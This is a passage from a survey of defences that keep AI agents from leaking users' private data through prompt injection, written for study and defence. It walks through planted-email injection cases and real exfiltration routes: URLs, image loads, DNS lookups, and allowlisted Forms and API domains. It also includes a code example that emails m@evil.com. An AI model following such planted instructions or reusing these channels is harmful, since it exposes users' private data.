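One reason for the poor result is that the filter passed or blocked each item whole. If an item was useful for the trip, all its private details went through with it, and 76.2% of attacks on useful items succeeded. The filter also worked from a task description so broad, covering activities, restaurants, preferences and insurance, that it can justify passing almost anything. The original study had found the same weakness. When the minimizer knew only the general domain, such as healthcare, average protection against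 plain questions fell from 96.8% to 68.6%. But 64.6% of attacks on data unrelated to the trip also succeeded, so the filter evidently made obvious mistakes too.

Abdelnabi and colleagues proposed two firewalls instead. The data abstraction firewall rewrites the user's data before the assistant receives it, so that a home address becomes "the Paris area" and an exact age becomes "adult". This firewall is a language model that receives only the raw data and a set of rules for the domain, so the outside agent's messages can't manipulate it. Another model writes the rules beforehand by comparing ordinary conversations with attacks.

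The language converter firewall filters messages coming in from the outside agent. A language model turns each message into a form with fixed fields, such as a price, a date or a room type. Ordinary code then deletes any field that isn't on the approved list and any value of the wrong type. Names can't be checked against a list, so the code replaces them with labels such as "hotel_3", which keeps instructions hidden in a hotel's name from reaching the assistant. An attacker might manipulate the model that fills in the form, but the code still removes whatever the form doesn't allow.

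Suppose the clinic's agent offers an appointment on Tuesday at ten, and adds that slots are going fast and that its insurer insists on a full medical summary. The converter would pass along only the available time, because the form has no field for the urgency or the insurer's demand.

Averaged over the three domains, the two firewalls cut the success rate of privacy attacks on GPT-5 from 84.7% to 10.2%. Attacks that tried to make the assistant act against the user's wishes, for example by exceeding a budget, fell from 60.4% to 3.4%. In travel planning, the researchers also tested each firewall alone against privacy attacks:

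| Protection for GPT-5 | Privacy attacks that succeeded | Parts of the task completed |
|---|---|---|
| None | 88.5% | 96.6% |
| Data abstraction only | 29.3% | 98.8% |
| Language conversion only | 20.7% | 95.6% |
| Both | 7.8% | 95.6% |

The two firewalls work best together, which makes sense because the first limits what the assistant knows and the second limits what outsiders can say to it. GPT-5 lost almost no utility, but Gemini 2.5 Pro completed about four percentage points less of the task.

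In most of the remaining privacy failures, the assistant gave the right kind of information in too much detail, such as "rock climbing and scuba diving" where "high-risk adventure activities" would have been enough. Better rules could fix many of these cases. None of the remaining failures involved an attacker defeating the code.

Privacy would be harder to protect in dentistry than in travel. The travel form can leave out requests for medical summaries because a hotel never needs one, but a dental form has to let the clinic ask about medical history, and an attacker can fill in that field as easily as the clinic can. Privacy in dentistry would therefore depend mostly on the abstraction firewall.

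### Requests that build on one another

Answering the same question repeatedly can reveal information that a single answer would protect. Suppose an assistant hides a patient's exact weight by adding new random noise each time someone asks. The outside party can average the answers to get a better estimate. After q independent answers, the typical error shrinks to about 1/√q of its original size, so 16 requests reduce it to about a quarter.

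Related questions have a similar effect. Body mass index (BMI) is weight divided by height squared. A service that receives noisy values for all three can use the height and BMI to estimate the weight a second time.

Anshumaan, Choudhary and colleagues (2026), in *Dependency-Aware Privacy for Multi-Turn LLM Agents*, analyse this with metric differential privacy. A method M that adds noise satisfies this standard if, for any two true values x and x′ and any set of outputs S,

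Pr[M(x) ∈ S] ≤ e^(ε·d(x, x′)) · Pr[M(x′) ∈ S],

where d is the distance between the values. A small ε means that nearby values produce nearly the same outputs, so an observer can hardly tell them apart. Each independent release of the same value adds another ε, and the guarantee weakens with every question. A derived value can cost more than ε, because a formula that changes steeply magnifies small differences in its inputs.

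Their system, RootGuard, adds noise to each original value once, at the start. It answers repeated questions with the same noisy value and calculates the BMI from the noisy height and weight. The service can't learn more from later questions than it could from the first noisy values.

The researchers tested this on real measurements from a US health survey. In one setting, ε was 0.1 for each value, the queries were spread over all the values, and the attacker knew the population averages. When the system drew fresh noise for each query, the attacker's average error fell from 10.2% to 3.2% as the number of queries rose from 1 to 16. When the system drew the noise once and divided it evenly, the error stayed at 13.2%.

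RootGuard adds noise only to numbers. It encrypts names and identifiers while keeping their format, and it depends on something else to identify the sensitive values correctly. Neither method would suit the penicillin allergy, which the dentist has to know exactly. But RootGuard's main idea, fixing an answer once and reusing it, would also help with abstraction. Abdelnabi and colleagues' firewall runs again each time the assistant retrieves data. If it described a user as "in their forties" on one turn and "under 45" on the next, the other side would learn that the user is between 40 and 44.

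Reusing answers doesn't prevent details from identifying someone when combined. Abdelnabi and colleagues acknowledge that a region, a family structure, an allergy and a set of unavailable dates may together identify a person, even though each is vague.

### Needs that appear midway

A minimizer chooses what to share with the assistant before the conversation starts, but the clinic's form may turn out to require an insurance number. *Privacy Preference Controls for Agentic Systems* (Kochar, Sugsavanvit and colleagues, 2026) lists as one open problem of data minimization how to grant an agent minimal access, without burdening the user, when nobody yet knows exactly what the agent will need.

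In *GapLeak*, Cheong, Zhang and colleagues (2026) studied what agents do at that point. They gave web agents a short summary for each of four tasks, one of them a medical intake form, and left out a fact that the form required. The agents could still open more sensitive files or account pages. The forms also suggested that extra information would be helpful, but contained no injected instructions.

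Many agents searched for the missing fact, found other private details, and entered those too. Across three agent programs, completed forms contained 38.6% of the details the researchers tracked about other people, such as relatives and emergency contacts. The score for excess information about the user was 36.2%. When the summary was complete and the form didn't encourage extra answers, the agents disclosed nothing improper.

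Telling the agents to stay away from the sensitive sources only partly worked. On the medical form, strict instructions stopped the improper disclosures, but the share of completed tasks fell from 41.7% to around 30%. The agents also kept opening the sensitive files, so the private data still entered their context, where a later injection could have reached it. AirGapAgent's separation would have denied the agents access to those files.

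It wouldn't have supplied the missing fact, though. In the job application task, three models invented an email address in every run instead of searching for the real one. An invented email address that gets rejected does little harm, but an invented answer about medicines could injure a patient. An assistant with restricted access therefore needs a reliable way to stop and ask for missing information.

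*The 2026 Singapore Consensus on Global AI Safety Research Priorities* (2026) recommends that an agent's access adjust as its task evolves, with explicit authorization for anything wider. It is safer for the agent to ask for that authorization before it opens the medical folder. As Cheong and colleagues note, a user who sees only the completed form is likely to approve it because it looks finished, and by then the agent has already read the files. Even when the agent asks early, the attacker may have written the reason that the user sees.

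Cheong and colleagues also had a separate model compare each finished form with the original summary and clear any optional field that the summary didn't support. This reduced excess information about the user from 32.4% to 1.2% without lowering task completion. The check didn't cover required fields, where GPT-5.4 sometimes put private details.

### Mixed documents and mailbox search

The dental table treats each fact as a separate item, but one letter from the family doctor may mention the penicillin allergy, the psychotherapy and the mother's illness. If the minimizer passes the letter, the clinic's agent may learn all three, and if it blocks the letter, the dentist may not hear about the allergy. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian warn that isolating even one critical piece of an email can make a task impossible.

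A tool can instead return only the relevant sentence. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) extends the principle of least privilege, an old rule in computer security, to tool output by limiting how much text the model receives and removing sensitive fields. *Minim* (Yu, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) applies a similar approach to agents that operate a screen. A program on the user's device scores every screen element by how sensitive it is and how necessary it is for the task, then removes elements before anything reaches the remote model. This can hide a visible login code or private notification.

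Access to a mailbox is even harder to limit, because the assistant often searches it to find out what it needs. *FORTIS* (2026) grades email tools by how much they can reach, from counting or searching message headers in one folder to a free-text search of the whole mailbox. For the check-up, a search limited to the clinic's address would exclude the user's bank statements and most planted emails. But it would miss a genuine reminder sent through an outside booking service, and it wouldn't help with a clinic the user has never contacted.

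### Selectors that err or read the attacker's text

Models are not very good at judging how little data they need. Zhou, Mireshghallah and Li (2025), in *Operationalizing Data Minimization for Privacy-Preserving LLM Prompting*, searched for the least revealing version of a prompt that still gave a good answer. GPT-5 could do without 85.7% of the sensitive details. But models asked to predict what they could do without tended to make details vaguer when they could have removed them, and so shared too much.

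The problem is more serious when the selector reads untrusted text. AirGapAgent's guarantee assumes that U, the user's own data, is trustworthy, and Abdelnabi and colleagues make the same assumption for their firewalls. A mailbox violates this assumption because anyone can send email to it. If the planted dental email is in U and states that new patients must supply their psychotherapy notes, the minimizer may read it and pass on the notes before the clinic has sent any message. Using a separate model doesn't by itself prevent this. *An AI Agent Execution Environment to Safeguard User Data* (2026) points out that "judge" models, which approve or block tool calls, are themselves open to injection if they read untrusted data.

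One solution is to treat the mailbox as an outside party. The minimizer would use only the user's request and a list of field names to choose fields from the calendar and the medical folder, and ordinary code would copy their values. The model that reads email would receive those values and have no way to retrieve more. The planted email could then expose the allergy and the blood thinner, but not the psychotherapy notes.

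This works only for data already sorted into fields. To extract one sentence from a doctor's letter, a model has to read the whole letter, including anything an attacker may have added. A selector that picks out smaller parts of documents may therefore have to read more untrusted text.

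## Tracking private data inside the system

Designers who use information-flow control assume that models will read attackers' text and sometimes be influenced by it. They label each piece of data with its source and who may receive it, and ordinary code outside the model checks those labels before the assistant takes any action with consequences.

The method is decades older than language models. *SPA* (2026), a paper on securing assistants that persist across requests, traces it to two classic computer security models. Bell–LaPadula keeps sensitive data from anyone not authorized to receive it, and Biba keeps unreliable data from influencing actions that need reliable inputs.

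### Labels and checks

Each piece of data x carries a label with two parts:

ℓ(x) = (R, I).

R, the confidentiality label, is the set of people who may receive x. I, the integrity label, is T (trusted) if x comes only from trusted sources, and U (untrusted) if an untrusted source may have influenced it. When the assistant derives something new from x and y, the result gets the join of their labels, written ⊔:

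ℓ(x) ⊔ ℓ(y) = (R_x ∩ R_y, I_x ⊔ I_y), where T ⊔ T = T and any join that includes U is U.

The join takes the stricter value for each part. If Ann and Ben may read one document, and Ben and Carol another, then a summary of both may go only to Ben. If either document contains even one untrusted paragraph, the whole summary is untrusted.

A model's output gets the join of the labels of everything in its context, because nobody can reliably tell which passages influenced the output. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) lists choosing which parts of the context to label separately among the method's open difficulties.

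Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, describe two basic checks on tool calls. Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, call them "trusted action" and "permitted flow":

- Trusted action: I = T for the context in which the model chose the call, and for every argument that has to be trustworthy.
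- Permitted flow: Q ⊆ R_d, where Q is the set of recipients and R_d is the set of people who may receive the data d.

Calls with no consequences, such as searching the user's calendar, need neither check. For calls that send data out, the designer can require both checks or accept either one.

The permitted-flow check alone doesn't stop an injection from making the assistant send an email, but it limits the recipients to people already allowed to receive the contents. Allowing an email that passes either check gives users more freedom. If a user asks the assistant to send the psychotherapy notes to a new therapist, the email can go out because the request is trusted, even though the therapist isn't on the notes' list of permitted recipients.

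The same freedom also allows the assistant to disclose private data by mistake. Suppose it has read nothing untrusted but misjudges what a dentist needs and puts the psychotherapy notes in the clinic's booking form. The trusted-action check passes, and the system sends the notes. The system protects against mistaken disclosures as well as induced ones only if its designer always requires the permitted-flow check.

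### A blocked email, and a blocked booking

For the dental appointment, the labels might look like this:

| Data | Who may receive it | Integrity |
|---|---|---|
| The user's request | Anyone | T |
| Penicillin allergy | User, clinic | T |
| Psychotherapy notes | User, therapist | T |
| Genuine email from the clinic | User, clinic | U |
| Planted email | User, attacker | U |

The emails' reader lists are based on Costa and colleagues' assumption that an email's sender and recipients may read it. The clinic's email is untrusted because anyone can write to the mailbox, and the software can't tell in advance which messages come from honest senders.

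The assistant searches the mailbox, and both emails enter its context. The set of permitted readers is now {user, clinic} ∩ {user, attacker} = {user}, and the integrity is U. The hidden paragraph persuades the model to open the psychotherapy notes, and the context's label stays at ({user}, U). The model then proposes

send_email(to = the records address, body = medical summary).

The trusted-action check fails because the context is untrusted. The permitted-flow check fails because the records address isn't in {user}. The code blocks the call no matter how persuasive the email is, because neither check depends on the wording.

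Next, the model tries to email the clinic the allergy and a few free times. It writes this email in the same context, so the email gets the same label and also fails both checks. The simplest form of tracking therefore protects the notes but also prevents the booking.

Costa and colleagues measured how often this happens by adding labels and checks to an ordinary assistant running on GPT-4o. With no attacker present, the share of AgentDojo's banking tasks it completed fell from 98.8% to 37.5%, and the share of Slack tasks fell from 93.3% to 20.0%.

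CaMeL and FIDES are attempts to keep the protection while letting the assistant complete more tasks. Both build on the dual-LLM pattern, which Willison proposed in 2023. In this pattern, a privileged model chooses the actions without ever reading untrusted text, which goes instead to a quarantined model that has no tools.

### CaMeL

Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues introduced CaMeL in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025). Its privileged model sees only the user's request and descriptions of the tools, and it writes the whole plan in advance as a program in a restricted form of Python. For the dental booking, it might write:

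```
times   = free_times("next week")
allergy = read_record("allergies")
mail    = search_mail("dentist")
address = ask_quarantined("What is the clinic's email address?", mail)
send_email(to=address, body=[times, allergy])
```

An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the program line by line. It tags every value with its sources and permitted readers (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026, *CaMeLoT*). Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, a short Python function that receives the call, its arguments and their tags, then allows or denies the call.

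The planted email can't add a line to this program, so no step opens the psychotherapy notes. It can still cause the quarantined model to return the attacker's address instead of the clinic's. The program would then send the allergy information to the attacker through a tool call the user wanted. CaMeL needs its policies to prevent this. The allergy information may go only to the user and the clinic, so the policy for send_email denies the call.

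*Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) defines the guarantee as control-flow integrity plus enforcement of the policies. Control-flow integrity means that only trusted inputs determine which tool calls the plan can contain. Untrusted data can determine which of the plan's existing branches runs, but it can't create a new one. The guarantee assumes that the user's request and the tool descriptions are trustworthy, that the labels and policies are right, and that the interpreter tracks every dependency.

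Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, reran CaMeL on AgentDojo's banking tasks. CaMeL blocked every attack with its policies on, but completed only about half as many tasks as with them off. With the policies off, 138 of 141 attacks in one category succeeded when CaMeL ran on MiMo-v2.5, so separating the two models is not enough to stop attacks.

Two other attacks defeated the separation itself. The user had asked the assistant to read a file and follow its instructions precisely, and the privileged model wrote a program that could call whichever tool the file named. An attacker could therefore choose the tool by writing the file.

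Committing to a plan in advance reduces the share of tasks an agent completes, even without policies. Peters-Gill and colleagues tested CaMeL agents on AssetOpsBench, a set of industrial maintenance tasks, with no policies in force. CaMeL lowered the share of completed tasks by an average of 21.6 percentage points across five models, and by 13.4 points for the two strongest, Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5. Most failures occurred because the need for another step became clear only after a tool returned its result. The researchers also had to document the exact format of every tool's output, since the privileged model writes code to process results without seeing them.

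### FIDES

FIDES, which Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, lets the planner work one step at a time, as ordinary assistants do. If adding a tool's result to the planner's context would make the context's label stricter, FIDES stores the result in a variable and shows the planner only the variable's name. The planner can pass the variable to another tool without reading its contents.

In the dental example, the planner would see that the search had found two emails, with names such as #email_1.body in place of their text. It could then do one of three things:

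1. Pass a variable on unread, for example to save the clinic's email in a folder.
2. Have a quarantined model answer a question about it, with the answer stored in another variable.
3. Open the variable and read it, which makes the context untrusted from then on.

If the planner opens the planted email, the attacker may take control of the planner. But opening the email also makes the context untrusted, so every later call fails the trusted-action check. The planner can then no longer send the psychotherapy notes to anyone outside the notes' list, even if the attacker controls it.

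FIDES can also limit how much information an answer may contain. If a task depends only on whether an email proposes a meeting, the planner can restrict the answer to yes or no. That is one bit of information, too little to contain an instruction, so a designer may decide that the answer is safe to act on even though it comes from untrusted text.

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo with GPT-4o. The table gives the share of tasks completed without an attacker.

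| Tasks | No labels or checks | Simple tracking with checks | FIDES with checks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Office | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% |
| Slack | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% |

The average completion rate over the four groups fell from 84% without protection to 42% with simple tracking and 50% with FIDES. Simple tracking did well on the travel tasks because many of their tools are allowed to run in an untrusted context as long as no confidential data leaves, whereas GPT-4o often mishandled FIDES's variables. With OpenAI's reasoning model o1, FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks.

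The unprotected assistant allowed 152 successful attacks, and FIDES allowed none. With its checks turned off, FIDES allowed 21, because nothing stopped the planner from opening a variable and following any instructions inside it.

The figure of zero depends on good labels. Costa and colleagues marked a field as untrusted if any of AgentDojo's attacks used it, so they knew where the attacks would come from. A company labelling its own data doesn't have that information. They also tested only one style of attack, but this matters less than usual because rewording an email doesn't change its label.

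*Flowsh* (Kim, Trampert and colleagues, 2026) extends label tracking to the shell, the command line through which many agents run programs and handle files. To test it against the strongest possible attacker, the researchers let the attacker choose the model's output once the planted text had reached the model. Flowsh still blocked all 40 attacks. Training the model to resist injection would not help in this test, because the attacker already controls its output.

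None of these systems guarantees that the text is accurate. A planted email can make the quarantined model return an empty or false summary, and FIDES will deliver it to a permitted recipient.

### When the next step is in an email

Costa and colleagues call a task data-dependent if the right sequence of actions depends on what the tools return. By their count, 5% of AgentDojo's office tasks are data-dependent, along with 10% of its travel tasks, 43.8% of its banking tasks and 42.9% of its Slack tasks. The dental booking becomes data-dependent when the clinic replies that new patients must fill in a form and supply an insurance number.

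CaMeL's planner can prepare for this by writing branches in advance, such as one for a clinic that asks for an insurance number. An attacker who controls the email can then choose which branch runs. If one branch sends the full medical history, the attacker may be able to trigger it without adding anything to the program, and only the policy on the email tool could stop the message.

*Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) relaxes the ban on tools for the model that reads untrusted text. Its subagent can keep calling tools after reading an email, but the labels restrict which calls it can make. This would work for a subagent that only has to look up free times, but it doesn't help when the email itself is the reason for sending something confidential.

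The hardest case is a request to follow the instructions in a document, such as paying the bill in a file. If an attacker replaces the file with a false bill, the assistant does what the user asked but pays the wrong person. Garby and colleagues' agent, Randori, failed in only two of 1,296 attacked runs, and both times its plan had marked an untrusted file as trusted. They report that an attack of the same kind succeeded in CaMeL's original evaluation, though CaMeL's developers consider it outside what the system is meant to prevent. If the file had not been marked as trusted, Randori would have blocked payment of the false bill, but it would also have blocked payment of a genuine one.

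### Asking the user

When a check fails, the system can ask the user instead of stopping. *PolicySniff* (2026) notes that CaMeL can ask the user to confirm a data flow that breaks a policy. Asking too often makes this safeguard less effective. According to Kim, Trampert and colleagues, Anthropic reports that users approve about 93% of the permission prompts in its coding tool Claude Code and pay less attention as the prompts accumulate.

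Kolluri and colleagues argue that earlier evaluations made label tracking look worse than it is. Those evaluations compared a protected assistant that couldn't ask for approval with an unprotected one that was free to act without it. Many unprotected assistants actually ask before every consequential action. When held to that practice, an ordinary assistant running on o3-mini completed 24.3% of AgentDojo's tasks without asking, compared with 35.5% for simple tracking and 50.1% for FIDES.

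The paper's own system, Prudentia, reached 59.1%. It is built on FIDES but gives the planner the labels and policies, so the planner can look for a route that breaks no policy. The planner must also give a reason before opening a variable. With o4-mini, Prudentia needed an average of 19.2 approvals to finish the benchmark, compared with 36.8 for FIDES, but completed slightly fewer tasks (73.2% against 75.7%).

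Prudentia can also ask the user to endorse a piece of data, which changes its label from untrusted to trusted. If a harmless email lists ten tasks for the assistant, the user can endorse the email once instead of approving ten separate actions.

Endorsement is also more dangerous. If the user endorses the planted dental email after glancing at its visible text, the hidden paragraph becomes trusted too, and every action that paragraph calls for passes the trusted-action check. Kolluri and colleagues assume in their experiments that users would catch attacks, and they leave the design of the prompts to later work.

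They decided not to offer the equivalent for confidentiality, called declassification, in which the user permits wider release of a piece of data. They argue that whether a release is appropriate depends heavily on the situation, so users should approve each one separately. Contextual integrity leads to the same conclusion, because a user who lets the dentist see the allergy hasn't agreed to show it to an employer.

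Flowsh reduced the number of approval requests further. Kim, Trampert and colleagues ran it with GPT-6.2 Sol on 17 office tasks, three times each, and on Terminal-Bench, a set of command-line tasks. For comparison, they gave another assistant the same tools without labels and had it ask for approval of every call it couldn't show to be safe. Flowsh needed 5.8 times fewer approvals per completed office task and 22.5 times fewer on Terminal-Bench. It completed 88.2% of the office runs, compared with 96.1% for the other assistant.

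Flowsh completed all 24 of the 51 office runs that didn't combine untrusted and confidential data, without asking anyone for approval. Of the 27 runs that did, it completed 21 when it could ask for approval and six when it couldn't. An AI assistant that reads a dental office's email and medical records would combine both kinds of data, so its user would still see about 2.5 approval prompts per completed task.

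Fewer approval requests may at least make each one more noticeable. In 39 of 45 runs with an attack, Flowsh's first request concerned the attack. However, the researchers simulated a perfect approver, and they say nobody has yet tested whether the information Flowsh provides helps real people decide. Flowsh also took 17–34% longer than the unlabelled assistant and used 17–55% more tokens.

Like the either-or rule described above, Flowsh's default policy allows confidential data to leave if nothing untrusted influenced the command. Removing that exception would also catch leaks caused by the model's own mistakes, but users would have to approve more harmless actions.

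### Who writes the labels

Someone has to supply the rules that all these systems enforce. In the dental example, the code lets the clinic receive the allergy only because someone put the clinic on the allergy's list. Label tracking still requires a judgment about appropriate sharing, which is difficult for models, but it moves that judgment to before any attacker can influence it.

The system also has to know which address belongs to the clinic. If the user's contacts include it, the label can refer to that entry. If the user has never contacted the clinic, the address will probably come from a web page or an email, and both are untrusted.

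Designers can fill some gaps with defaults. Flowsh can treat any file without a label as untrusted and readable only by the user, which is safe but leads to more prompts. Costa and colleagues suggest that a system could trust an email's sender address when the mail server has authenticated it. They also mention marking a document as trusted after running it through an injection detector, but warn that this weakens the guarantee because detectors make mistakes.

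A list of readers also describes a privacy norm only crudely. It covers the receiver and the type of information, but it can't express the condition that the dentist may use the allergy information only for treatment. A single label on a mixed document, such as the family doctor's letter, also leaves the same all-or-nothing choice that the minimizer had.

Some policies set the order of events, such as requiring the assistant to ask the user before it opens the medical folder. CaMeL evaluates its policies one tool call at a time, which makes such rules awkward to express. Nikolaou and colleagues' CaMeLoT translates CaMeL's program into a diagram of every path the program could take and checks all the paths before any tool runs. If a path breaks a rule, the privileged model gets a description of that path and can rewrite the program. CaMeLoT may reject some safe programs because it assumes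 a loop could run any number of times.

Labels must also last as long as the data. Flowsh stores each file's label with the file, so the restriction still applies when the assistant opens the file in a new conversation months later. Applied to an assistant's memories, the same approach would keep the old conversation about panic attacks out of an email to the dentist, if someone had labelled it correctly at the time.

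In May, Microsoft added FIDES to Agent Framework, its toolkit for building agents, as an experimental feature (Microsoft, 2026). FIDES's confidentiality labels are public, private and user identity, according to Microsoft's documentation. A developer who marks every medical record "private" would give the allergy and the psychotherapy notes the same protection, so a useful dental assistant would need finer labels.

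### What the choice of action reveals

Suppose an assistant opens a clinic's web page only if the user's notes mention psychotherapy. The request contains no medical data, but whoever runs the website can learn something about the user from the visit. Computer scientists call this an implicit flow.

FIDES doesn't prevent implicit flows. Its formal guarantee, explicit secrecy, requires that the steps the assistant took would produce results that look the same to an outsider if only the secrets in the stored data were different. Because this definition holds the steps fixed, it doesn't cover what an outsider could learn from which steps the assistant took. The guarantee also doesn't cover timing or the size of network messages.

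A stronger property, non-interference, also covers the choice of steps. Costa and colleagues rejected it as too restrictive because it would effectively ban any publicly visible action after the assistant has read something secret. Once the dental assistant had opened the medical folder, for example, it could not load the clinic's website.

*PolicySniff* describes three such leaks that CaMeL's developers examined: a web request that depends on a secret, an error that changes what the program visibly does next, and a program that measures time with a clock. CaMeL's strict mode handles the first two by labelling whatever depends on a secret condition. CaMeL's interpreter prevents the third by not giving programs a clock.

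Garby and colleagues found a gap that this tracking misses. It takes a few lines of code, where the balance is secret and the other values start out public:

```
rich = True
poor = True
if balance > threshold: poor = False
if poor: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, the program sets `poor` to `False` and the interpreter marks `poor` as secret. The program then skips the line that would change `rich`. Because the interpreter marks a variable as secret only when it runs an assignment to that variable, `rich` remains public and the program sends the email. If the balance is low, the program sends no email. Either way, the attacker learns whether the balance is above the threshold.

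An attacker can't simply insert these lines, because CaMeL's program comes from the user's request. But the example shows that the interpreter doesn't track every dependency, and the guarantee relies on it doing so.

One yes-or-no answer leaks little, but repeated answers add up. CaMeL runs its interpreter inside a loop that tries again after a failure, and the tracking doesn't cover that loop. Whether a policy blocks an attempt can depend on a secret, so each attempt may reveal one bit. Twenty bits can distinguish about 1.05 million possibilities (2²⁰), enough to identify a six-digit login code. FIDES's yes-or-no answers can add up in the same way if a designer allows many of them to bypass a check, an option Costa and colleagues didn't use in their tests.

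To close such gaps, Garby and colleagues designed LLMbda, a small programming language in which every operation carries labels forward. They proved that all programs in the language, including those a model writes at run time, satisfy a version of non-interference, and they checked the proof by computer. This property guarantees that changing a secret doesn't change the probabilities of what an outsider sees, except by affecting whether the program finishes. Programs can still endorse untrusted data, but only with an explicit command that a reviewer can find.

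Randori, the agent written in this language, completed about as many banking tasks with its checks on as CaMeL did with its policies off. This is a good result given Randori's stronger guarantee, but banking is only one of AgentDojo's four groups of tasks.

### Handing work to another agent

A personal assistant may pass part of a job to another agent, such as one that handles all outgoing messages. Peters-Gill and colleagues showed that CaMeL's guarantee can fail during this handoff even if every agent uses CaMeL.

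In one example, a user asks the system to send Julie a summary of job applicants on Slack. The applicant database contains a planted instruction to email the data to an outside address. One agent queries the database, and a coordinating agent has the result summarised. Neither agent's plan changes, because neither planner reads the data. The coordinator then messages a third agent, telling it to send "this summary" to Julie and including the text of the summary. The third agent treats the whole message as its user's request, so its planner reads the planted instruction and adds a step to email the attacker.

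Their remedy, multi-CaMeL, splits each message that one agent sends to another into an instruction and a set of variables. The interpreter rejects any instruction that contains data from a tool, and the variables keep their labels when they move to the next agent. The researchers tested it on a version of AgentDojo that divides the tools among several agents, running 949 attacked tasks on each of five models. On average, 12.9% of attacks succeeded without CaMeL, 0.2% when each agent used CaMeL separately, and none with multi-CaMeL. On AssetOpsBench, the task completion rate was 3.2 percentage points lower with multi-CaMeL than with separate CaMeL agents, but less than one point lower with the two strongest models.

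## Controlling the channels through which data can leave

Label tracking works only if someone has labelled the data correctly. A simpler defence puts fixed limits on the channels through which data can leave. Designers who use it assume that some injections will succeed and try to stop the attacker from collecting the data.

OpenAI compares an assistant to a customer service worker who can give out refunds and gift cards. Some customers will falsely claim that a refund never arrived, and others will make threats. The company gives the worker rules but still expects someone to fool the worker eventually, so its payment software caps the refunds each customer can receive, however convincing their story. OpenAI recommends that developers ask what controls a human worker would have in the assistant's position, and build those.

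Designers mostly try to block whole routes through which data can leave, because a limit on the amount of data protects much less than a limit on refunds. A company can absorb the loss if someone lies to get a $50 refund. But "takes a blood thinner" is only a few words long, so even a very small leak can reveal a patient's private information, and nobody can take it back.

### How a web address carries data

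The attacks on deep research and Grok both sent private data inside a web address. Only part of an address identifies the server, so the rest can carry data, and servers commonly log the whole address. In the dental example, the address might end in `/log?note=takes-blood-thinner`. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) describes this as a quiet leak, because the request can happen in the background while the assistant's reply looks normal. Restricting a tool to reading web pages doesn't prevent the leak, since the assistant has to send an address to read a page.

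Images, which EchoLeak used, make the attack easier because the chat window requests them without a click. Rehberger reported this weakness to OpenAI and Microsoft in early 2023, according to *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, a post on his blog, Embrace The Red. Microsoft blocked such images that May. OpenAI added a first check in December, but Rehberger found ways around it, and OpenAI strengthened the check in about August 2025.

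Messaging apps can do the same with ordinary links. When a link appears in Slack or Telegram, the app may load the page to show a preview. PromptArmor's *Threat Intelligence* warns that an assistant talking to its user through such an app can leak data as soon as it writes a link.

Even looking up a server's name can leak data. Before a computer contacts a server, it asks the Domain Name System (DNS), the internet's directory, where to find it. The query can reach a computer controlled by the domain's owner, so an attacker who owns a domain can receive data hidden in the name. ChatGPT's sandbox for running Python blocked ordinary internet connections but still allowed these lookups. Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (2026) describes using them to steal data through a custom version of ChatGPT that posed as a personal doctor. A user uploaded lab results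 and described symptoms, and the attackers' server received the patient's name and the model's medical assessment. When the user asked whether the data had been sent anywhere, ChatGPT said it had not. OpenAI finished its fix on February 20, 2026.

Users seldom have any way to notice a leak. In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) had an assistant running on Qwen2.5-7B summarise web pages that contained planted instructions. The assistant contacted the attackers' server in 423 of 480 runs, and in 95% of the successful attacks its summary gave no sign that it had done so. The high success rate is weak evidence of how often current assistants would leak data, because the model was small and the researchers had placed the secrets directly in its context. But a stronger model that did follow the instructions could hide the leak just as well.

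### Lists of allowed destinations

The most direct control is an allowlist, a list of the only domains that the assistant's software may contact. Lan, Kaul and colleagues compared one with defences that rely on the model, using 30 attacked runs for each:

| Protection | Runs in which a request reached the attacker |
|---|---|
| None | 100% |
| Tags that mark web content as untrusted | 100% |
| An instruction never to obey web content | 66.7% |
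| Tags and instruction together | 56.7% |
| Domain allowlist | 0% |

With the allowlist on, the model still tried to contact the attacker in every run, and the software blocked every attempt. The block worked without any resistance from the model, but only because the attacker used a domain that was plainly not on the list. Real attackers look for an allowed domain that will accept the stolen data, and researchers have found several.

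Web applications often put their allowlist in a content security policy, which limits where the user's browser can load images and scripts from. Superhuman, the email assistant that leaked its users' messages, had a policy that allowed images from the Google domain that hosts Google Docs and Google Forms. A Google form can record an answer contained in a web address. The planted email made the assistant write an image address that would submit the user's emails to the attacker's form when the browser loaded it. PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* shows the stolen emails among the form's responses. PromptArmor's *Codex for Everything Exfiltrates Connected Data* describes the same trick against OpenAI's Codex, which PromptArmor reported in April, after Superhuman's fix. OpenAI has since fixed that too.

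A list can also go out of date. Salesforce's policy for its assistant Agentforce still allowed a domain that had expired. In September 2025, according to Willison, researchers at Noma Security registered the domain and received data about a company's sales leads. Salesforce corrected the list and added a check that stops the agent from generating links to untrusted domains. Google made a different mistake with Antigravity, whose default list included a public service that records incoming requests for anyone who sets up a page there.

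Claude Cowork, Anthropic's assistant for office work, allowed connections to Anthropic's own programming interface, a seemingly safe destination where anyone can open an account. In PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files*, the planted instructions contained the attacker's access key, and Cowork used it to upload the user's files to the attacker's Anthropic account. PromptArmor published this two days after Cowork's release in January 2026. Rehberger had already described the weakness in another Claude product in 2025, in Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate*. According to *The Read-Only Lie*, on the blog אִם יִרְצֶה הַשֵּׁם, Anthropic tightened Cowork's permissions afterwards.

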